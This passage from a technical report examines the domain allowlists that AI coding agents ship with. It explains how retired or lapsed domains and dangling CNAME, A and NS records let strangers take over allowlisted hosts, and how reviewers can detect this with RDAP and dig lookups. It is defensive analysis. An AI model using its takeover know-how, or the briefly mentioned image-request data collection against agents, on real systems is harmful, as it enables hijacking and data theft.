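The number of entries in a list is a poor guide to how many hosts it allows. Codex's list has a third as many entries as Copilot's but probably allows more hosts. For example, OpenAI lists debian.org, while GitHub lists four specific hosts under that domain, including deb.debian.org. OpenAI doesn't say whether an entry covers subdomains, but the preset would be of little use for installing software if entries didn't cover them.

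The lists also differ in how they treat shared storage. GitHub allows storage.googleapis.com, Google's storage service, only for certain paths, such as the one that holds an archive for the Dart programming language. Anthropic's Claude Code list allows `*.googleapis.com` and `*.amazonaws.com` without restricting the path.

To check registrations, the reviewer can reduce each list to its registrable domains. Codex's 71 entries reduce to 67 because some share a domain, as packages.microsoft.com and mcr.microsoft.com share microsoft.com. Claude Science's list will take more care than its length suggests because it includes many research databases with their own domains, such as pheweb.jp and civicdb.org, and a small project may find it harder than a large company to keep renewing a domain.

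Defaults determine who is exposed to an old entry. GitHub turns on Copilot's recommended list by default, and a new Claude Code environment starts with Anthropic's list. Codex applies its list only if the user opts in.

Only OpenAI promises updates, saying it will keep the Codex preset current "based on feedback and as the tooling ecosystem evolves". Its page listed the same 71 entries in May and September 2026. A list that hasn't changed in four months isn't necessarily neglected, but three of the entries belong to services that had closed or changed their names years earlier.

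Anthropic makes no such promise for Claude Code, yet it edited that list between July and November 2026. It removed the entries for Statsig and Sentry, which provide analytics and error reporting, and added others, including a wildcard for Cloudflare's storage service. Two entries for retired names, jcenter.bintray.com and continuum.io, were still there in November, so recent changes to a list are weak evidence that anyone has reviewed all of it.

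### Worked example: retired names in the Codex and Copilot lists

A useful first pass is to mark every entry whose service has closed or changed its name. Four services stand out in the Codex and Copilot presets:

| Service | Codex entry | Copilot entries | What happened to the service | Who controls the name |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| RubyForge | rubyforge.org | gems.rubyforge.org | Closed in May 2014 | No current holder established |
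| JCenter | jcenter.bintray.com | jcenter.bintray.com | Closed in August 2024 | JFrog, as of August 2024 |
| Continuum Analytics | continuum.io | repo.continuum.io | Became Anaconda in 2017 | In use for the company's mailing list in March 2018; no current holder established |
| Binstar | None | binstar.org, conda.binstar.org | Apparently became Anaconda.org | No current holder established |

**RubyForge** hosted projects written in the Ruby programming language. In 2009, Ruby Central, the organization behind it, said that other sites did much of this work better and that it would focus on RubyGems.org (Kilmer, 2009, *RubyForge and RubyGems and GemCutter*). RubyForge shut down on May 15, 2014. FreshPorts' *rubygem rubyforge* shows that maintainers of the FreeBSD operating system were removing references to it by that August.

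The subdomain on Copilot's list, gems.rubyforge.org, lasted longer. Förster (2014) reported in June 2014 that it had become an alias for rubygems.org, the live service. The alias would work only as long as the holder of rubyforge.org maintained it.

JFrog's **JCenter** service distributed Java software. In April 2021 JFrog announced that it would keep JCenter online "indefinitely" as a read-only service (JFrog's *Into the Sunset on May 1st* (2021)). But three years later, JFrog's *JCenter Sunset on August 15th, 2024* (2024) set a closing date and said that all requests for jcenter.bintray.com would be redirected to Maven Central, the main public source of Java packages. Of the four names, jcenter.bintray.com is the best documented, because JFrog needed control of it to redirect the traffic.

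**Continuum Analytics**, a data-science software company, announced in 2017 that it was renaming itself Anaconda, after its main product. It planned to move its default package source from repo.continuum.io to repo.anaconda.com in March 2018 (Anaconda). That month a user complained that an old download page no longer worked, and someone replied that the company was finally shutting off its old web properties (okiror jethro (2018), in *problem downloading anaconda*). The mailing list they were using still had a continuum.io address, so the domain was still in use then.

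**Binstar** has the least documentation. Copilot's list includes binstar.org and conda.binstar.org next to the matching anaconda.org names, which is consistent with a name change. The 2017 python4oceanographers notebook *Binstar/conda package stats* also uses "Binstar" in connection with Anaconda.org.

A service can be retired without its domain lapsing, because the owner can keep renewing the name to redirect visitors, as JFrog does, or to keep strangers from buying it. No published report shows that any of these four names is open to registration. The marks only show the reviewer which names to look up first, since a company has less reason to renew a name it has stopped using.

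An active project's domain can also be unsafe. In April 2009, when the programming framework Ruby on Rails was in wide use, visitors to rubyonrails.org found a spam page. In the forum thread *It looks like a domain squatter grabbed rubyonrails.org* (2009), a participant quoted the framework's creator, who blamed the company that managed the registration and said it had parked the domain "again". The registration had been due for renewal on April 19, and its record changed on April 23.

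The name is now on the Codex, Kiro and Claude Code lists. Its registration runs until April 2032, according to cside's *rubyonrails.org*, so it looks much safer today. A reviewer who looked only for defunct services would not have checked it.

### What the Kiro and Codex lists have in common

Kiro's preset contains all 71 Codex entries, spelled the same way, and adds only amazonaws.com and aws.amazon.com, both Amazon domains. Both lists are alphabetical, so the matching order is not further evidence of copying.

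Some overlap is natural, because any list for installing software will include pypi.org for Python and npmjs.org for JavaScript. But both lists also include unusual entries (RubyForge, JCenter and Continuum), and both name packages.microsoft.com and ppa.launchpad.net even though they already include microsoft.com and launchpad.net. Two teams working independently would be unlikely to make all the same choices, so either one company copied the other's list or both used the same source.

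Overlap with the other presets suggests that the shared source may be older or more widely used. Of the 71 Codex entries, 59 also appear word for word in Claude Code's July 2026 list, including the three retired names, and 34 appear word for word in Copilot's. GitHub often lists a specific host where OpenAI lists the whole domain, so the overlap with Copilot's list is larger when entries are compared by registrable domain. By that measure, 67 of the 71 Codex entries have a match, and the exceptions are bitbucket.org, gitlab.com, hex.pm and sourceforge.net.

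RubyForge is the strongest clue to the list's origin. It closed eleven years before OpenAI launched its Codex cloud agent in 2025, so the agent can't have needed it. The domain probably came from an older list or old configuration files, but a language model could also have included it when drafting the list from its training data. None of the companies has explained where its list came from, and the overlap between the lists doesn't show who copied whom.

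Agreement between vendors is weak evidence that an entry is sound. If they copied from one another or from a common source, the same domain on four lists may reflect one decision that nobody has revisited. Each company also has to remove a bad entry from its own list, so a correction by OpenAI would not protect Kiro's users.

### How website allowlists decayed

Roth and colleagues traced website allowlists from 2012 to 2018. They found that more than 13% of the sites that tried to restrict scripts had allowed a domain that had expired, contained an obvious typing error or pointed to a private address, which works only inside a local network. That figure covers all three faults, not just expired domains.

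The study also shows that site owners found policies hard to maintain. Of 449 sites that tried a content policy in report-only mode, where the browser reports violations without blocking anything, 251 never enforced one. Across the whole period, 1,233 sites enforced a CSP of some kind on at least one day, but only 1,032 did so in the final month. Some owners tried for months to keep their allowlists current before giving up.

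Old entries probably survive in part because removing a domain that is still needed breaks something immediately and users complain, whereas leaving an unneeded one on the list causes no visible trouble unless a stranger acquires it.

That incentive probably applies to AI vendors too, but the 13% figure doesn't. Those websites each wrote a policy for their own pages, which often load content from many advertisers and other partners. An AI vendor maintains one preset for all its customers, so it has fewer lists to check, but a single lapsed domain would affect every customer who uses the preset.

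## Checking whether a listed domain's registration has lapsed

Registration records are public, so a reviewer can check the domains on an allowlist without the vendor's help. Two kinds of company keep these records. A registry runs a whole ending, as Verisign does for .com, and a registrar such as GoDaddy sells names to the public. The check has five steps:

1. Reduce the entry to its registrable domain.
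2. Ask the registry for its record of that domain.
3. If there is no record, ask a registrar whether the name is for sale.
4. If there is a record, read its status codes, expiry date, creation date and registrar.
5. Compare the creation date with a date on which the expected owner certainly held the name.

It is tempting to skip the comparison of dates, but without it a domain that a stranger has already bought looks perfectly healthy.

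### From an entry to a registrable domain

The reviewer first removes any `*.`, port or path from the entry, then finds the registrable domain, which is the part of the name that somebody registered. For cdn.example.com this is example.com, but for cdn.example.co.uk it is example.co.uk, because British companies register names under co.uk. Since counting dots can't distinguish these cases, software uses the Public Suffix List, a volunteer-maintained list of the endings under which people can register names. The registrable domain is the longest matching ending plus one label to its left.

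The list also has a private section for domains such as github.io, whose owners give subdomains to their customers. Browsers use that section to keep customers' sites apart. A reviewer should turn it off for this check, because GitHub registered only github.io and no registry has a record for somebody.github.io.

Some entries from the lists in earlier sections reduce as follows:

| Entry | Where it appears | Domain to look up |
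|---|---|---|
| `*.my-salesforce-cms.com` | Salesforce's old CSP header | my-salesforce-cms.com |
| gems.rubyforge.org | Copilot preset | rubyforge.org |
| jcenter.bintray.com | Codex preset | bintray.com |
| `usagereports*.blob.core.windows.net` | GitHub's firewall instructions | windows.net |

The last entry needs a separate check, because a stranger could hold a storage account that matches it even if Microsoft's registration of windows.net is current. The two IP addresses in Copilot's preset have no domain registration.

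### Reading the registry's record

The current way to query a registry is the Registration Data Access Protocol (RDAP), the successor to WHOIS. ICANN, which coordinates the domain name system, made RDAP the definitive source of registration data for generic endings such as .com and .org on January 28, 2025 (ICANN, 2025). Many registries and registrars then began shutting down their WHOIS services, according to APNIC's *The current state of RDAP* (2026). An old script that treats an empty WHOIS reply as "unregistered" may therefore flag registered domains as lapsed.

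ICANN has a lookup page for single names. For a long list of .com names, a reviewer can query Verisign directly:

`curl -si https://rdap.verisign.com/com/v1/domain/example.com`

A 404 error means the registry has no record of the name. Anyone can then probably register it, but registries reserve some names, so the reviewer should confirm with a registrar. If there is a record, its `status` field contains the status codes, `events` contains the creation date (under "registration") and the expiry date, and `entities` includes the registrar.

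ICANN's *EPP Status Codes* explains the codes. These are the ones that matter most here:

| RDAP status | Meaning | Conclusion |
|---|---|---|
| active | Nothing is pending | Registered, so check the creation date |
| client transfer prohibited | The registrar has locked the name against transfers | Normal for a well-kept domain |
| auto renew period | The expiry date has passed and the registry has extended the registration | The registrar may still cancel the extension |
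| client hold, server hold | The registrar or registry has kept the name out of DNS, perhaps over a dispute or an unpaid bill | Registered, but ask the owner why |
| inactive | The name has no name servers, the machines that answer DNS queries for it | Registered, but it won't resolve |
| redemption period | The registrar has asked the registry to delete the name | The old holder has at most 30 days to recover it |
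| pending delete | The recovery period is over, unless "redemption period" also appears | Anyone can register the name within days |

### What happens to a .com name after it expires

An expired domain has not yet lapsed in the sense that anyone may register it. It first goes through three stages:

| Stage | Length | Who can get the name | Does it resolve? |
|---|---|---|---|
| Auto-renew grace period | Up to 45 days | The old holder, or a buyer if the registrar auctions it | Often, at least at first |
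| Redemption period | 30 days | The old holder | No |
| Pending delete | 5 days | Nobody | No |

On the expiry date, the registry automatically extends an unrenewed registration by a year. During a grace period, which an ICANN working paper gives as 45 days, the registrar can cancel this extension without paying for it. ICANN's *Expired Registration Recovery Policy* allows the registrar to delete the registration at any time after expiry.

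The release date therefore depends on when the registrar acts. ICANN's policy uses the example of a name that expires on October 1 and that the registrar deletes on October 20. The redemption period would then run to November 19, and a stranger could register the name on November 24. Here is that case with the earliest and latest normal ones:

| Registrar deletes the name | Redemption ends | First day a stranger can register it | Days after expiry |
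|---|---|---|---|
| October 1 | October 31 | November 5 | 35 |
| October 20 | November 19 | November 24 | 54 |
| November 15 | December 15 | December 20 | 80 |

In *WHOIS Lost in Translation*, Lauinger, Onarlioglu and colleagues (2016) found that new registrations rose most steeply 78 and 79 days after expiry, slightly before the 80-day mark, which is the only figure many explanations give. Registrars apparently delete names slightly early to avoid the renewal fee. A much smaller rise began around day 35, probably because some registrars had deleted names on the expiry date.

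A stranger can also get the name before its release. Some registrars auction their customers' expired names during the grace period, and the winner takes over the existing registration. *Game of Registrars* (Lauinger, Chaabane and colleagues, 2017) reports that GoDaddy started such auctions on the 26th day after expiry. If a name expired on October 1 and the registrar planned to delete it on November 15, bidding could open on October 27, nearly eight weeks before the name would otherwise be released on December 20.

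### Country-code domains

This timetable doesn't apply to country-code endings such as .uk, .jp and .io, whose registries set their own rules. Infoblox (2026), a DNS security vendor, notes that some of these endings have shorter recovery periods or no redemption period. An Australian .au name, for example, becomes eligible for deletion the day after its renewal grace period ends (ds.network's *Domain Name Life Cycles*). *Domain-Z* (Lever, Walls and colleagues, 2016) described how Canada's registry auctioned expiring .ca names before their general release.

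Country-code registries may use the same status codes with other meanings, or use different codes, so the registrar OpenSRS recommends looking up the codes on the registry's own website. Many of these registries also don't publish creation dates, which are the best evidence that a name has changed owners.

The AI presets contain several names with country-code endings, including continuum.io in the Codex list and pheweb.jp in the Claude Science list. A reviewer should read the rules for each ending before deciding how long an expired name stays safe.

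### Why a DNS lookup isn't enough

Checking only whether each name resolves, meaning that DNS returns an address for it, saves time but can miss lapsed registrations and flag active ones as lapsed.

An expired name may still resolve because ICANN requires registrars to interrupt its normal DNS service only for the last eight days in which the old holder can renew it. If the registrar waits the full 45 days before deletion, a name that expired on October 1 could work normally into early November. Even during the interruption, the registrar may point the name to its own web page. That page must say that the registration has expired, but the notice is only useful to a person who reads it, not to a browser fetching an image or an agent running an installer.

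The opposite error is to conclude that a registration has lapsed because the name has no DNS records. Lever and colleagues warn that an NXDOMAIN reply, meaning the name is not in DNS, doesn't show that the name is available to register. They checked availability with the registry through a domain reseller's account. Lauinger and colleagues followed 5.3 million .com names after the names vanished from DNS, and found that about 6% either had not expired or had been renewed.

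An owner also can't rely on somebody noticing the outage. When the image editor GIMP failed to renew gimp.org, users reported the problem within days and the project recovered the name. But Infoblox describes a case in which major media websites kept a marketing service's content-delivery domain in their pages after it expired. Requests to the domain failed for years, apparently without anyone noticing. In February 2026 a criminal group registered it and began sending the sites' visitors to malware.

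A domain whose own registration is current can also be affected if the domain of one of its name servers expires. In 2012, bobbroadband.com expired while two of its hosts were name servers for Benedictine University's ben.edu. The university had other name servers, so the expiry caused no obvious outage. A search-marketing company then bought bobbroadband.com, and its servers answered some queries for ben.edu with the address of an advertising site. A reviewer can find a listed domain's name servers in its RDAP record and run the same registration check on the name servers' domains.

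### Using dates to detect a new owner

An RDAP record is better evidence than a DNS lookup, but its expiry date can be misleading. The .com registry automatically adds a year, so a name that nobody has renewed may show an expiry date almost a year ahead. The "auto renew period" status should identify such names, but only .org showed it among the five top-level domains that Lauinger and colleagues studied in 2015 and 2016.

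If the expiry date is between about 320 and 365 days away, the domain may still be in its grace period, and the reviewer should look it up again 45 days later. If the creation date is unchanged and neither "redemption period" nor "pending delete" appears, someone has paid for the extension, usually the old owner but possibly the winner of an auction.

A name that a stranger has re-registered is harder to spot because it has a normal status, a distant expiry date and working DNS. Its creation date usually reveals the change, because the registry starts a new record when someone registers a deleted name. If the creation date is after the vendor added the entry, the registration that the vendor trusted has ended. The version history of a configuration file or archived copies of the vendor's documentation may show when the vendor added the entry.

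However, the entry's date is a safe baseline only if whoever added the entry checked the domain at the time. Suppose a stranger had bought rubyforge.org in 2020 and OpenAI had copied the name from an old list in 2025. The domain's creation date would be five years earlier than the entry, so the domain would pass the check.

It is safer to compare the creation date with the last date the expected owner is known to have used the domain. For rubyforge.org, this could be June 2014, when gems.rubyforge.org still led to the live RubyGems service. For continuum.io, it could be March 2018, when the company's mailing list was on that domain. If either domain has a later creation date, its registration has ended at least once since then.

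The check can raise a false alarm when an owner loses a domain and later gets it back. If Salesforce recovered my-salesforce-cms.com by taking over Noma's registration, the record would still show the date Noma bought it.

More seriously, names sold before deletion keep their original creation date. In four weeks of 2016, Lauinger and colleagues counted 1.2 million .com names on the lists of four auction services. About 70,600 stayed registered afterwards, and the researchers believe only a small fraction of these were late renewals by the old owner. They also found that new registrants took 334,300 .com names after deletion. On these figures, the creation-date check would have missed up to one takeover in six. The true share could be higher, because the four lists did not cover every auction.

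To catch these sales, a reviewer needs earlier observations for comparison. Lever and colleagues designed an algorithm called Alembic that looks for ownership changes in stored DNS traffic. For each date, it compares a period before with a period after and adds three scores, each between 0 and 1:

- **Addresses:** 1 − |A ∩ B| / |A ∪ B|, where A and B are the sets of network addresses that the name led to before and after. A move to entirely new addresses scores 1. Replacing one of two addresses scores 2/3.
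- **Traffic:** One minus the p-value of a t-test on the number of lookups, so a clear change in traffic scores close to 1.
- **Administration:** Half the score depends on changes to the main name server in the domain's DNS settings and half on changes to the contact email address.

A total near 3 suggests a new owner. A domain could also score highly if its existing owner moves to another hosting company, so a high total is a reason to investigate but doesn't prove a sale. Lauinger and colleagues doubt that Alembic would detect every auction sale, since the buyer may keep the same registrar or hosting company and change little in DNS.

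Most reviewers don't have years of DNS traffic records, but they can save each domain's registrar and name servers and compare them at the next check. If either has changed shortly after an expiry date, it is worth calling the supposed owner.

### How quickly strangers take lapsed names

Most lapsed names stay unregistered for months, but buyers take the most attractive ones almost immediately. In their 2016 study, Lauinger and colleagues followed 7.4 million names under .com, .net, .org, .biz and .name that had disappeared from DNS, checking their WHOIS records every two weeks. Of the 6.5 million that had expired in the usual way, new registrants took about 16.5% during the study.

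The researchers had observed some names for longer than others, so they used survival analysis to estimate the share not yet re-registered after a given number of days. About 20% of .com names were re-registered within 300 days of expiry. About as many names were re-registered in the first 80 days as in the next 270, even though most did not become available until near the end of those 80 days.

A .com name dropped after at least nine years was about three times as likely to be re-registered by someone else as one dropped after a year. The average may therefore understate the risk for long-lived services in AI presets.

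In the 2017 study, Lauinger and colleagues looked more closely at the day of deletion. They combined several services' published lists of names awaiting deletion and checked WHOIS before and after the names were released. New registrants took 10.1% of deleted .com names on the same day, compared with 6.6% for .net, 4.7% for .org and 1.8% for .biz. They took another 5% of the .com names over about the next month.

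Much of this speed comes from drop-catch services, which send automated registration requests the moment a domain is released. More than half of the same-day .org registrations happened within 30 seconds. So a company that finds a valuable listed domain in "pending delete" can't count on buying it by hand. Noma's $5 purchase suggests that no drop-catch service wanted my-salesforce-cms.com, at least when the researchers found it.

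### What new holders do with the names

A new holder is not necessarily an attacker. Many re-registered domains carry only advertisements or a for-sale notice. Several studies have tried to measure how many are used for abuse, but each study's methods could detect only certain kinds.

Lever and colleagues assembled about 179 million expired domains from November 2008 to July 2015, mainly by comparing successive copies of the registries' lists of names. They then searched for these domains in eight public blacklists and in records of the addresses that malware contacted when researchers ran it. This yielded two main figures:

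| Evidence of abuse | Domains in the data | First appeared there after expiring | Share |
|---|---|---|---|
| Public blacklists | 320,009 | 27,758 | 8.7% |
| Contact by malware | 6,112,964 | 238,279 | 3.9% |

The blacklist figure is stronger evidence of abuse than contact by malware, which the researchers call an indicator, not a guarantee, because people had curated the blacklists. There were 784 blacklisted cases from 2009 to 2012 and more than 9,000 in 2014 alone, though blacklists can also grow because their maintainers look harder.

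Their case studies more closely resemble the problem with AI allowlists. In about 40,000 browser plugins, they found 159 expired domains that anyone could register. They also describe debian-multimedia.org, an unofficial software source that many users of the Debian operating system had added to their update settings. The owner moved to a new domain and let the old one expire, and an unknown party registered it. Debian's maintainers had to ask users to delete the old entry by hand.

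Automated requests are a large part of the danger. In *Domains Do Change Their Spots*, Miramirkhani and colleagues (2022) point out that system updates, as well as people browsing the web, can connect to an expired domain without detecting that it has a new owner. They registered 201 expired domains and found that substantial traffic still arrived.

The most recent study used DNS traffic from companies. In 2026, Muzammil, Ansari and colleagues, in *Echoes of the Past*, presented EchoLoc, a system that finds re-registered domains and judges whether they are malicious. It works in four stages:

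1. EchoLoc takes each newly registered domain from a WHOIS feed and searches older records for an earlier creation date.
2. It checks whether any of Infoblox's business customers have looked up the domain since its re-registration.
3. If they have and Infoblox doesn't already list the domain as malicious, EchoLoc saves the web page and a screenshot. It groups similar sites so that it can examine one from each group.
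4. OpenAI's GPT-4o rates the threat, and a second model combines that rating with features of the page to reach a verdict.

A security professional labeled 2,000 sites by hand to train and test the second model. In tests, 95% of the sites it flagged as malicious were malicious, and it detected 95% of the malicious sites.

EchoLoc found 1.5 million re-registered domains over 32 days in July and August 2025. Customers had looked up about 66,000 of them, and EchoLoc and Infoblox's existing data together identified 9,171 of those (13.9%) as malicious. Of the malicious domains, 3,841 were new to Infoblox, including 3,039 gambling sites.

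Some of the other 86% would also be unsafe on an allowlist. EchoLoc classifies a domain by what its website displays, and it discards a domain that still has no website after a week. Someone collecting data from image requests needs only a server that logs the requested addresses, as in ForcedLeak. That server could show a harmless page or nothing.

One of the domains EchoLoc found, netdna-ssl.com, is more like an allowlist entry than the gambling sites are. It had belonged to a content delivery network, and many websites loaded scripts and style sheets from its subdomains. The new holder redirected visitors to a video-downloading site. Infoblox saw 2.25 million lookups of 15,225 host names from 1,121 customers, though these totals include traffic from before the change. A site with `*.netdna-ssl.com` in its CSP would have allowed requests to the new holder's servers.

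The paper gives July 24, 2025 as the date netdna-ssl.com expired. A .com name that expired that day could not have been open to new registration until August 28 at the earliest, by which time the study had ended. July 24 is more likely the day the registry released the name.

Infoblox later estimated that an average of 50,400 domains a day were re-registered under generic endings in the first half of 2026, or around 65,000 including the country-code endings for which it had data. It counts a re-registration when a domain it has seen before reappears with a new creation date. These figures leave out names that changed hands before deletion and names under endings that don't publish creation dates, so the true number of takeovers is probably higher.

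Infoblox's result is broadly in line with EchoLoc's average of 46,600 a day in 2025, but both rely on Infoblox's data, and some Infoblox employees co-wrote EchoLoc. The two sources disagree about the share of all registrations, which is about 20% according to Infoblox but 1% of 144.6 million according to EchoLoc. At Infoblox's rate, there would be only about 10 million registrations in 32 days, so the 144.6 million probably includes records that weren't new registrations.

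Some criminals pay heavily for previously used domains. Infoblox's *$7 Million in Expired Domains Fuel a Streaming Empire* (2026) profiles a group it calls Sable Squirrel, which runs illegal sports streaming and gambling sites and uses some of the same domains to control malware. Infoblox found prices for about 160 of the group's purchases, totaling more than $430,000. Extrapolating from these, it estimated that the group had spent over $7 million.

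That estimate covers only one group of attackers and depends on the 160 names being typical. Those names cost about $2,700 each on average, so $7 million would buy around 2,600. The true total is lower if prices were easier to find for expensive names.

The group took a median of about five days to activate a domain after buying it. One of the domains, veinteractive.com, had belonged to an advertising company that collapsed in 2017, and thousands of other websites still contact it every day. Most of the purchases that Infoblox priced went through GoDaddy. If GoDaddy sold those domains before deletion, as it did with other expired names in 2017, they kept their old creation dates, and a reviewer comparing dates would have missed the change of owner.

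## Checking whether a listed subdomain can be taken over

A company can keep renewing example.com and still lose control of cdn.example.com to a stranger if it gives up the resource behind the subdomain but leaves a dangling DNS record. The registration checks in the previous section can't detect this because the registration hasn't changed.

Three types of record matter most for an allowlist:

| Record | What it does | How it comes to dangle |
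|---|---|---|
| CNAME | Makes one name an alias for another | The owner deletes the cloud site behind the alias, or the domain behind it lapses |
| A | Gives the network address (IP address) of a server | The owner shuts down a rented server, and the provider gives its address to someone else |
| NS | Names a server that answers DNS queries for the subdomain | The owner closes its account with the DNS provider, or the name server's domain lapses |

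The command `dig cdn.example.com` follows a name's aliases to its final address. What the reviewer should do next depends on the type of record.

### An alias to a deleted cloud resource

In February 2025, a hijacker took over a subdomain of the US Centers for Disease Control and Prevention (CDC). The subdomain was an alias for a website on Azure, Microsoft's cloud service:

`ahbazuretestapp.cdc.gov` → `ahbdotnetappwithsqldb.azurewebsites.net`

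Portal and Burton (2025), in *Cloudy with a Chance of Hijacking Forgotten DNS Records Enable Scam Actor*, concluded that the CDC had abandoned its Azure site without deleting the DNS alias that pointed to it. Because Azure customers choose the first part of a site's address, anyone could then open an Azure account, create a site with the same name and control what the CDC subdomain displayed.

Some hosting services, such as Shopify, have many customers share one address. A shop can make shop.example.com an alias for that address, then enter shop.example.com in its Shopify account so that visitors see the right shop. If the owner closes the account but keeps the alias, another customer may be able to enter the same name. In 2016, Liu, Hao and Wang reported in *All Your DNS Records Point to Us* that most services of this kind did not check who owned the name.

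An alias can also point to a lapsed domain. Portal and Burton give the example of marthastewart.msn.com, an alias for the unregistered domain msnmarthastewartsweeps.com. A spammer registered that domain for a few dollars and could then send email as MSN. A reviewer should therefore run the registration check on every domain in a chain of aliases.

An NXDOMAIN reply at the end of the chain is a strong warning, but its absence proves little. Most cloud providers return an IP address even when the customer's resource no longer exists, so the reviewer also needs to request the page and read the error message. Lin, Lin and colleagues (2024), in *Detecting and Measuring Security Implications of Entangled Domain Verification in CDN*, collected these replies from content delivery networks (CDNs), which serve copies of websites from machines around the world. Six of them look like this:

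| CDN | Reply after the customer has left |
|---|---|
| Azure | NXDOMAIN |
| G-core | SERVFAIL, a DNS error |
| KuaikuaiCloud | 127.0.0.1, the address a computer uses for itself |
| Bunny | Web error 403 with "Domain suspended or not configured" |
| Fastly | Web error 500 with "Fastly error: unknown domain" |
| Netlify | Web error 404 with "Not Found - Request ID" |

A matching reply suggests the customer has left, but doesn't show that a stranger can claim the name. Fastly and G-core, for instance, fixed the flaw after the researchers reported it. A reviewer who doesn't own the domain shouldn't test this by claiming the name, because that would itself be a takeover. It is better to tell the owner which record looks abandoned.

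Cloud providers can prevent these takeovers by making customers prove that they control a domain, for example by adding a random code to its DNS records. Of the 45 CDNs that Lin and colleagues tested, 39 required no proof and 19 allowed a stranger to take over an abandoned subdomain. Some of the others presumably assign addresses that a stranger can't reproduce.

Random addresses seem to help prevent takeovers. In *Cloudy with a Chance of Cyberattacks*, Frieß, Gattermayer and colleagues (2024) monitored cloud-hosted names for three years and found hijacks only where customers could choose the name of the resource. They found none on Google Cloud, which assigned names at random. But the names must be unpredictable. Two CDNs, Kuocai and Yundun, generated the same supposedly random address whenever anyone added the same domain, so an attacker could reproduce the victim's. Frieß and colleagues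 also recommend that providers stop new customers from reusing recently released names.

A reviewer shouldn't assume that the provider prevents takeovers. According to Portal and Burton, Azure has protections against hijacking even where a dangling record exists, yet the CDC lost its subdomain through Azure. Baidu, Bunny, Cachefly and UCloud acknowledged the flaw that Lin and colleagues reported, but said they aren't responsible for how customers configure their services.

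### An address record to a released cloud server

A company that rents a virtual server may use an A record to point a subdomain at the server's IP address. If the company later shuts down the server but forgets to delete the record, the provider can give the address to another customer, who then receives the subdomain's traffic.

An attacker can rent and release addresses repeatedly until they get the one the subdomain points to. *Cloud Strife* (Borgolte, Fiebig et al., 2018) estimates that this would cost less than $1 and take an aggressive attacker under 70 seconds. DNS servers often keep an old answer for longer than that, so an owner who deletes the record and releases the address at the same time may still be exposed for a short time. It is safer to delete the record first, wait for the old answers to expire and then release the address.

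Cloud providers publish their address ranges, so a reviewer can tell whether an A record points to a cloud address. It is much harder to tell whether the domain's owner still rents that address. The owner's server may be running but not reply to test messages, and a server that does reply may belong to a customer who rented the address later.

The choice of test also affects the result. When Frieß and colleagues tested the hijacked names in their data, 72% responded to a ping (a test message), while 89% responded to a request for the web page. A reviewer using only pings would have wrongly judged about a fifth of the working sites to be abandoned. The owner can settle the question by comparing its A records with the addresses in its cloud account, but an outsider has to ask the owner.

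The provider's main protection is to assign addresses at random from a large pool. It could also wait a while before reusing released addresses, but Liu and colleagues found in 2016 that Amazon and Microsoft made them available again immediately.

Attackers seem to prefer easier targets than released IP addresses. Frieß and colleagues monitored A records that pointed into clouds and found no hijack through a released address. They attribute this to cost and effort, since an attacker can claim an abandoned Azure site by typing its name. The finding is reassuring about mass abuse, but less so about a host on an AI vendor's allowlist, because a single address there might be worth many attempts.

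### A delegation to an abandoned name server

An owner can also delegate a subdomain such as lab.example.com by adding NS records that name another DNS provider's servers, which then answer all queries for it. If the owner closes the account at that provider but keeps the NS records, an attacker may be able to open an account there and set up lab.example.com as their own. The attacker can then create any name under lab.example.com and point it to any server.

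The command `dig +trace lab.example.com` shows which name servers the parent domain lists. The reviewer can then query each one directly:

`dig @ns1.provider.example lab.example.com SOA`

A working name server returns a record for the subdomain, while one that no longer serves it usually returns REFUSED or SERVFAIL, or doesn't respond. The reviewer should test every listed server, because Unit 42 warns that one dangling NS record among several can be enough for a takeover. An attacker can flood the other servers with traffic so that queries go to the one they control. The reviewer should also check that the name servers' own domains haven't lapsed, as bobbroadband.com had.

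The same failure can affect a whole registered domain. In what Infoblox calls a "Sitting Ducks" attack, someone hijacks the domain at its DNS or web hosting provider. Portal and Burton of Infoblox write that random sampling turns up thousands of potentially vulnerable domains every day and that attackers have hijacked tens of thousands since 2020.

Registration checks can miss a domain hijacked at its DNS provider, because its creation date, registrar and listed name servers can all stay the same. The reviewer should therefore query the name servers of every registrable domain on the allowlist, even if the list has no entries for delegated subdomains.

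A DNS provider can protect former customers by requiring proof of control before it answers for a domain. It can also randomly assign name servers to each new account, so an attacker may need many attempts to get the right ones.

### Why a wildcard entry widens the task

The reviewer only has to test one host for an exact entry. The entry `*.example.com` trusts every subdomain, including any forgotten test site. In Copilot, a custom entry for `example.com` also covers all its subdomains, even without an asterisk.

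Here is an illustration. Suppose example.com has 200 subdomains and each has the same chance, p, of being open to takeover, independently of the others. An exact entry is unsafe with probability p, but the wildcard is unsafe with probability 1 − (1 − p)^200:

| Assumed p | Expected number of unsafe subdomains | Chance that an exact entry is unsafe | Chance that the wildcard is unsafe |
|---|---|---|---|
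| 1% | 2 | 1% | 87% |
| 0.1% | 0.2 | 0.1% | 18% |
| 0.006% | 0.012 | 0.006% | 1.2% |

The last row is close to a measured rate. *Can I Take Your Subdomain?* scanned about 26 million subdomains of 50,000 popular sites and confirmed that 1,520 were open to takeover. That count excludes subdomains that pointed to apparently unused cloud addresses, so the true rate may be higher.

Real dangling records also cluster, which the formula doesn't account for. About 0.7% of the subdomains in that scan were at least potentially vulnerable, including those pointing to apparently unused addresses. Only 28% of the sites had such a subdomain, whereas a random spread would have put at least one on nearly every site with the average of 520 subdomains. The risk of a wildcard therefore depends heavily on the size of the domain and on how well its owner maintains its DNS records. Among .edu domains, which had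 6,033 subdomains on average, 7.3% had at least one confirmed case, compared with 1.8% of .com domains.

To test a wildcard, the reviewer first needs a list of subdomains. The domain's owner can export one from its DNS settings. Outsiders can collect names from search engines, records of past DNS traffic and Certificate Transparency logs, which are public records of issued certificates. An outsider's list will rarely be complete, so finding no problems is weaker evidence of safety for a wildcard than for an exact entry.

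Even a complete list can miss names that nobody has used yet. An owner may use a DNS wildcard record to send every name under project.example.com to a hosting service. An attacker might then invent evil.project.example.com and claim it at that service. *Can I Take Your Subdomain?* reports flaws in the ownership checks of 17 of the 21 services the researchers could test. To find a wildcard record, the reviewer can look up a made-up name, such as `x7q2k9.project.example.com`, and see whether it resolves.

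Some owners deliberately give subdomains to strangers. The researchers found that institutions in eduroam, a network that lets students and academics get online at other universities, sometimes assign each visitor's device a name under their main domain. A wildcard entry for such a domain would allow connections to visitors' laptops, though a firewall might keep outsiders from reaching them. This matters for products such as Claude Science, whose allowlist includes research databases and wildcards.

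An attacker can also exploit a trusted subdomain without taking it over. A 2026 report describes such an attack on Anthropic's Claude browser extension, which trusted Anthropic's subdomains as a group. The attack relied on a script flaw in one of those subdomains, which a test for dangling records would not have found.

### Why the counts of vulnerable subdomains differ

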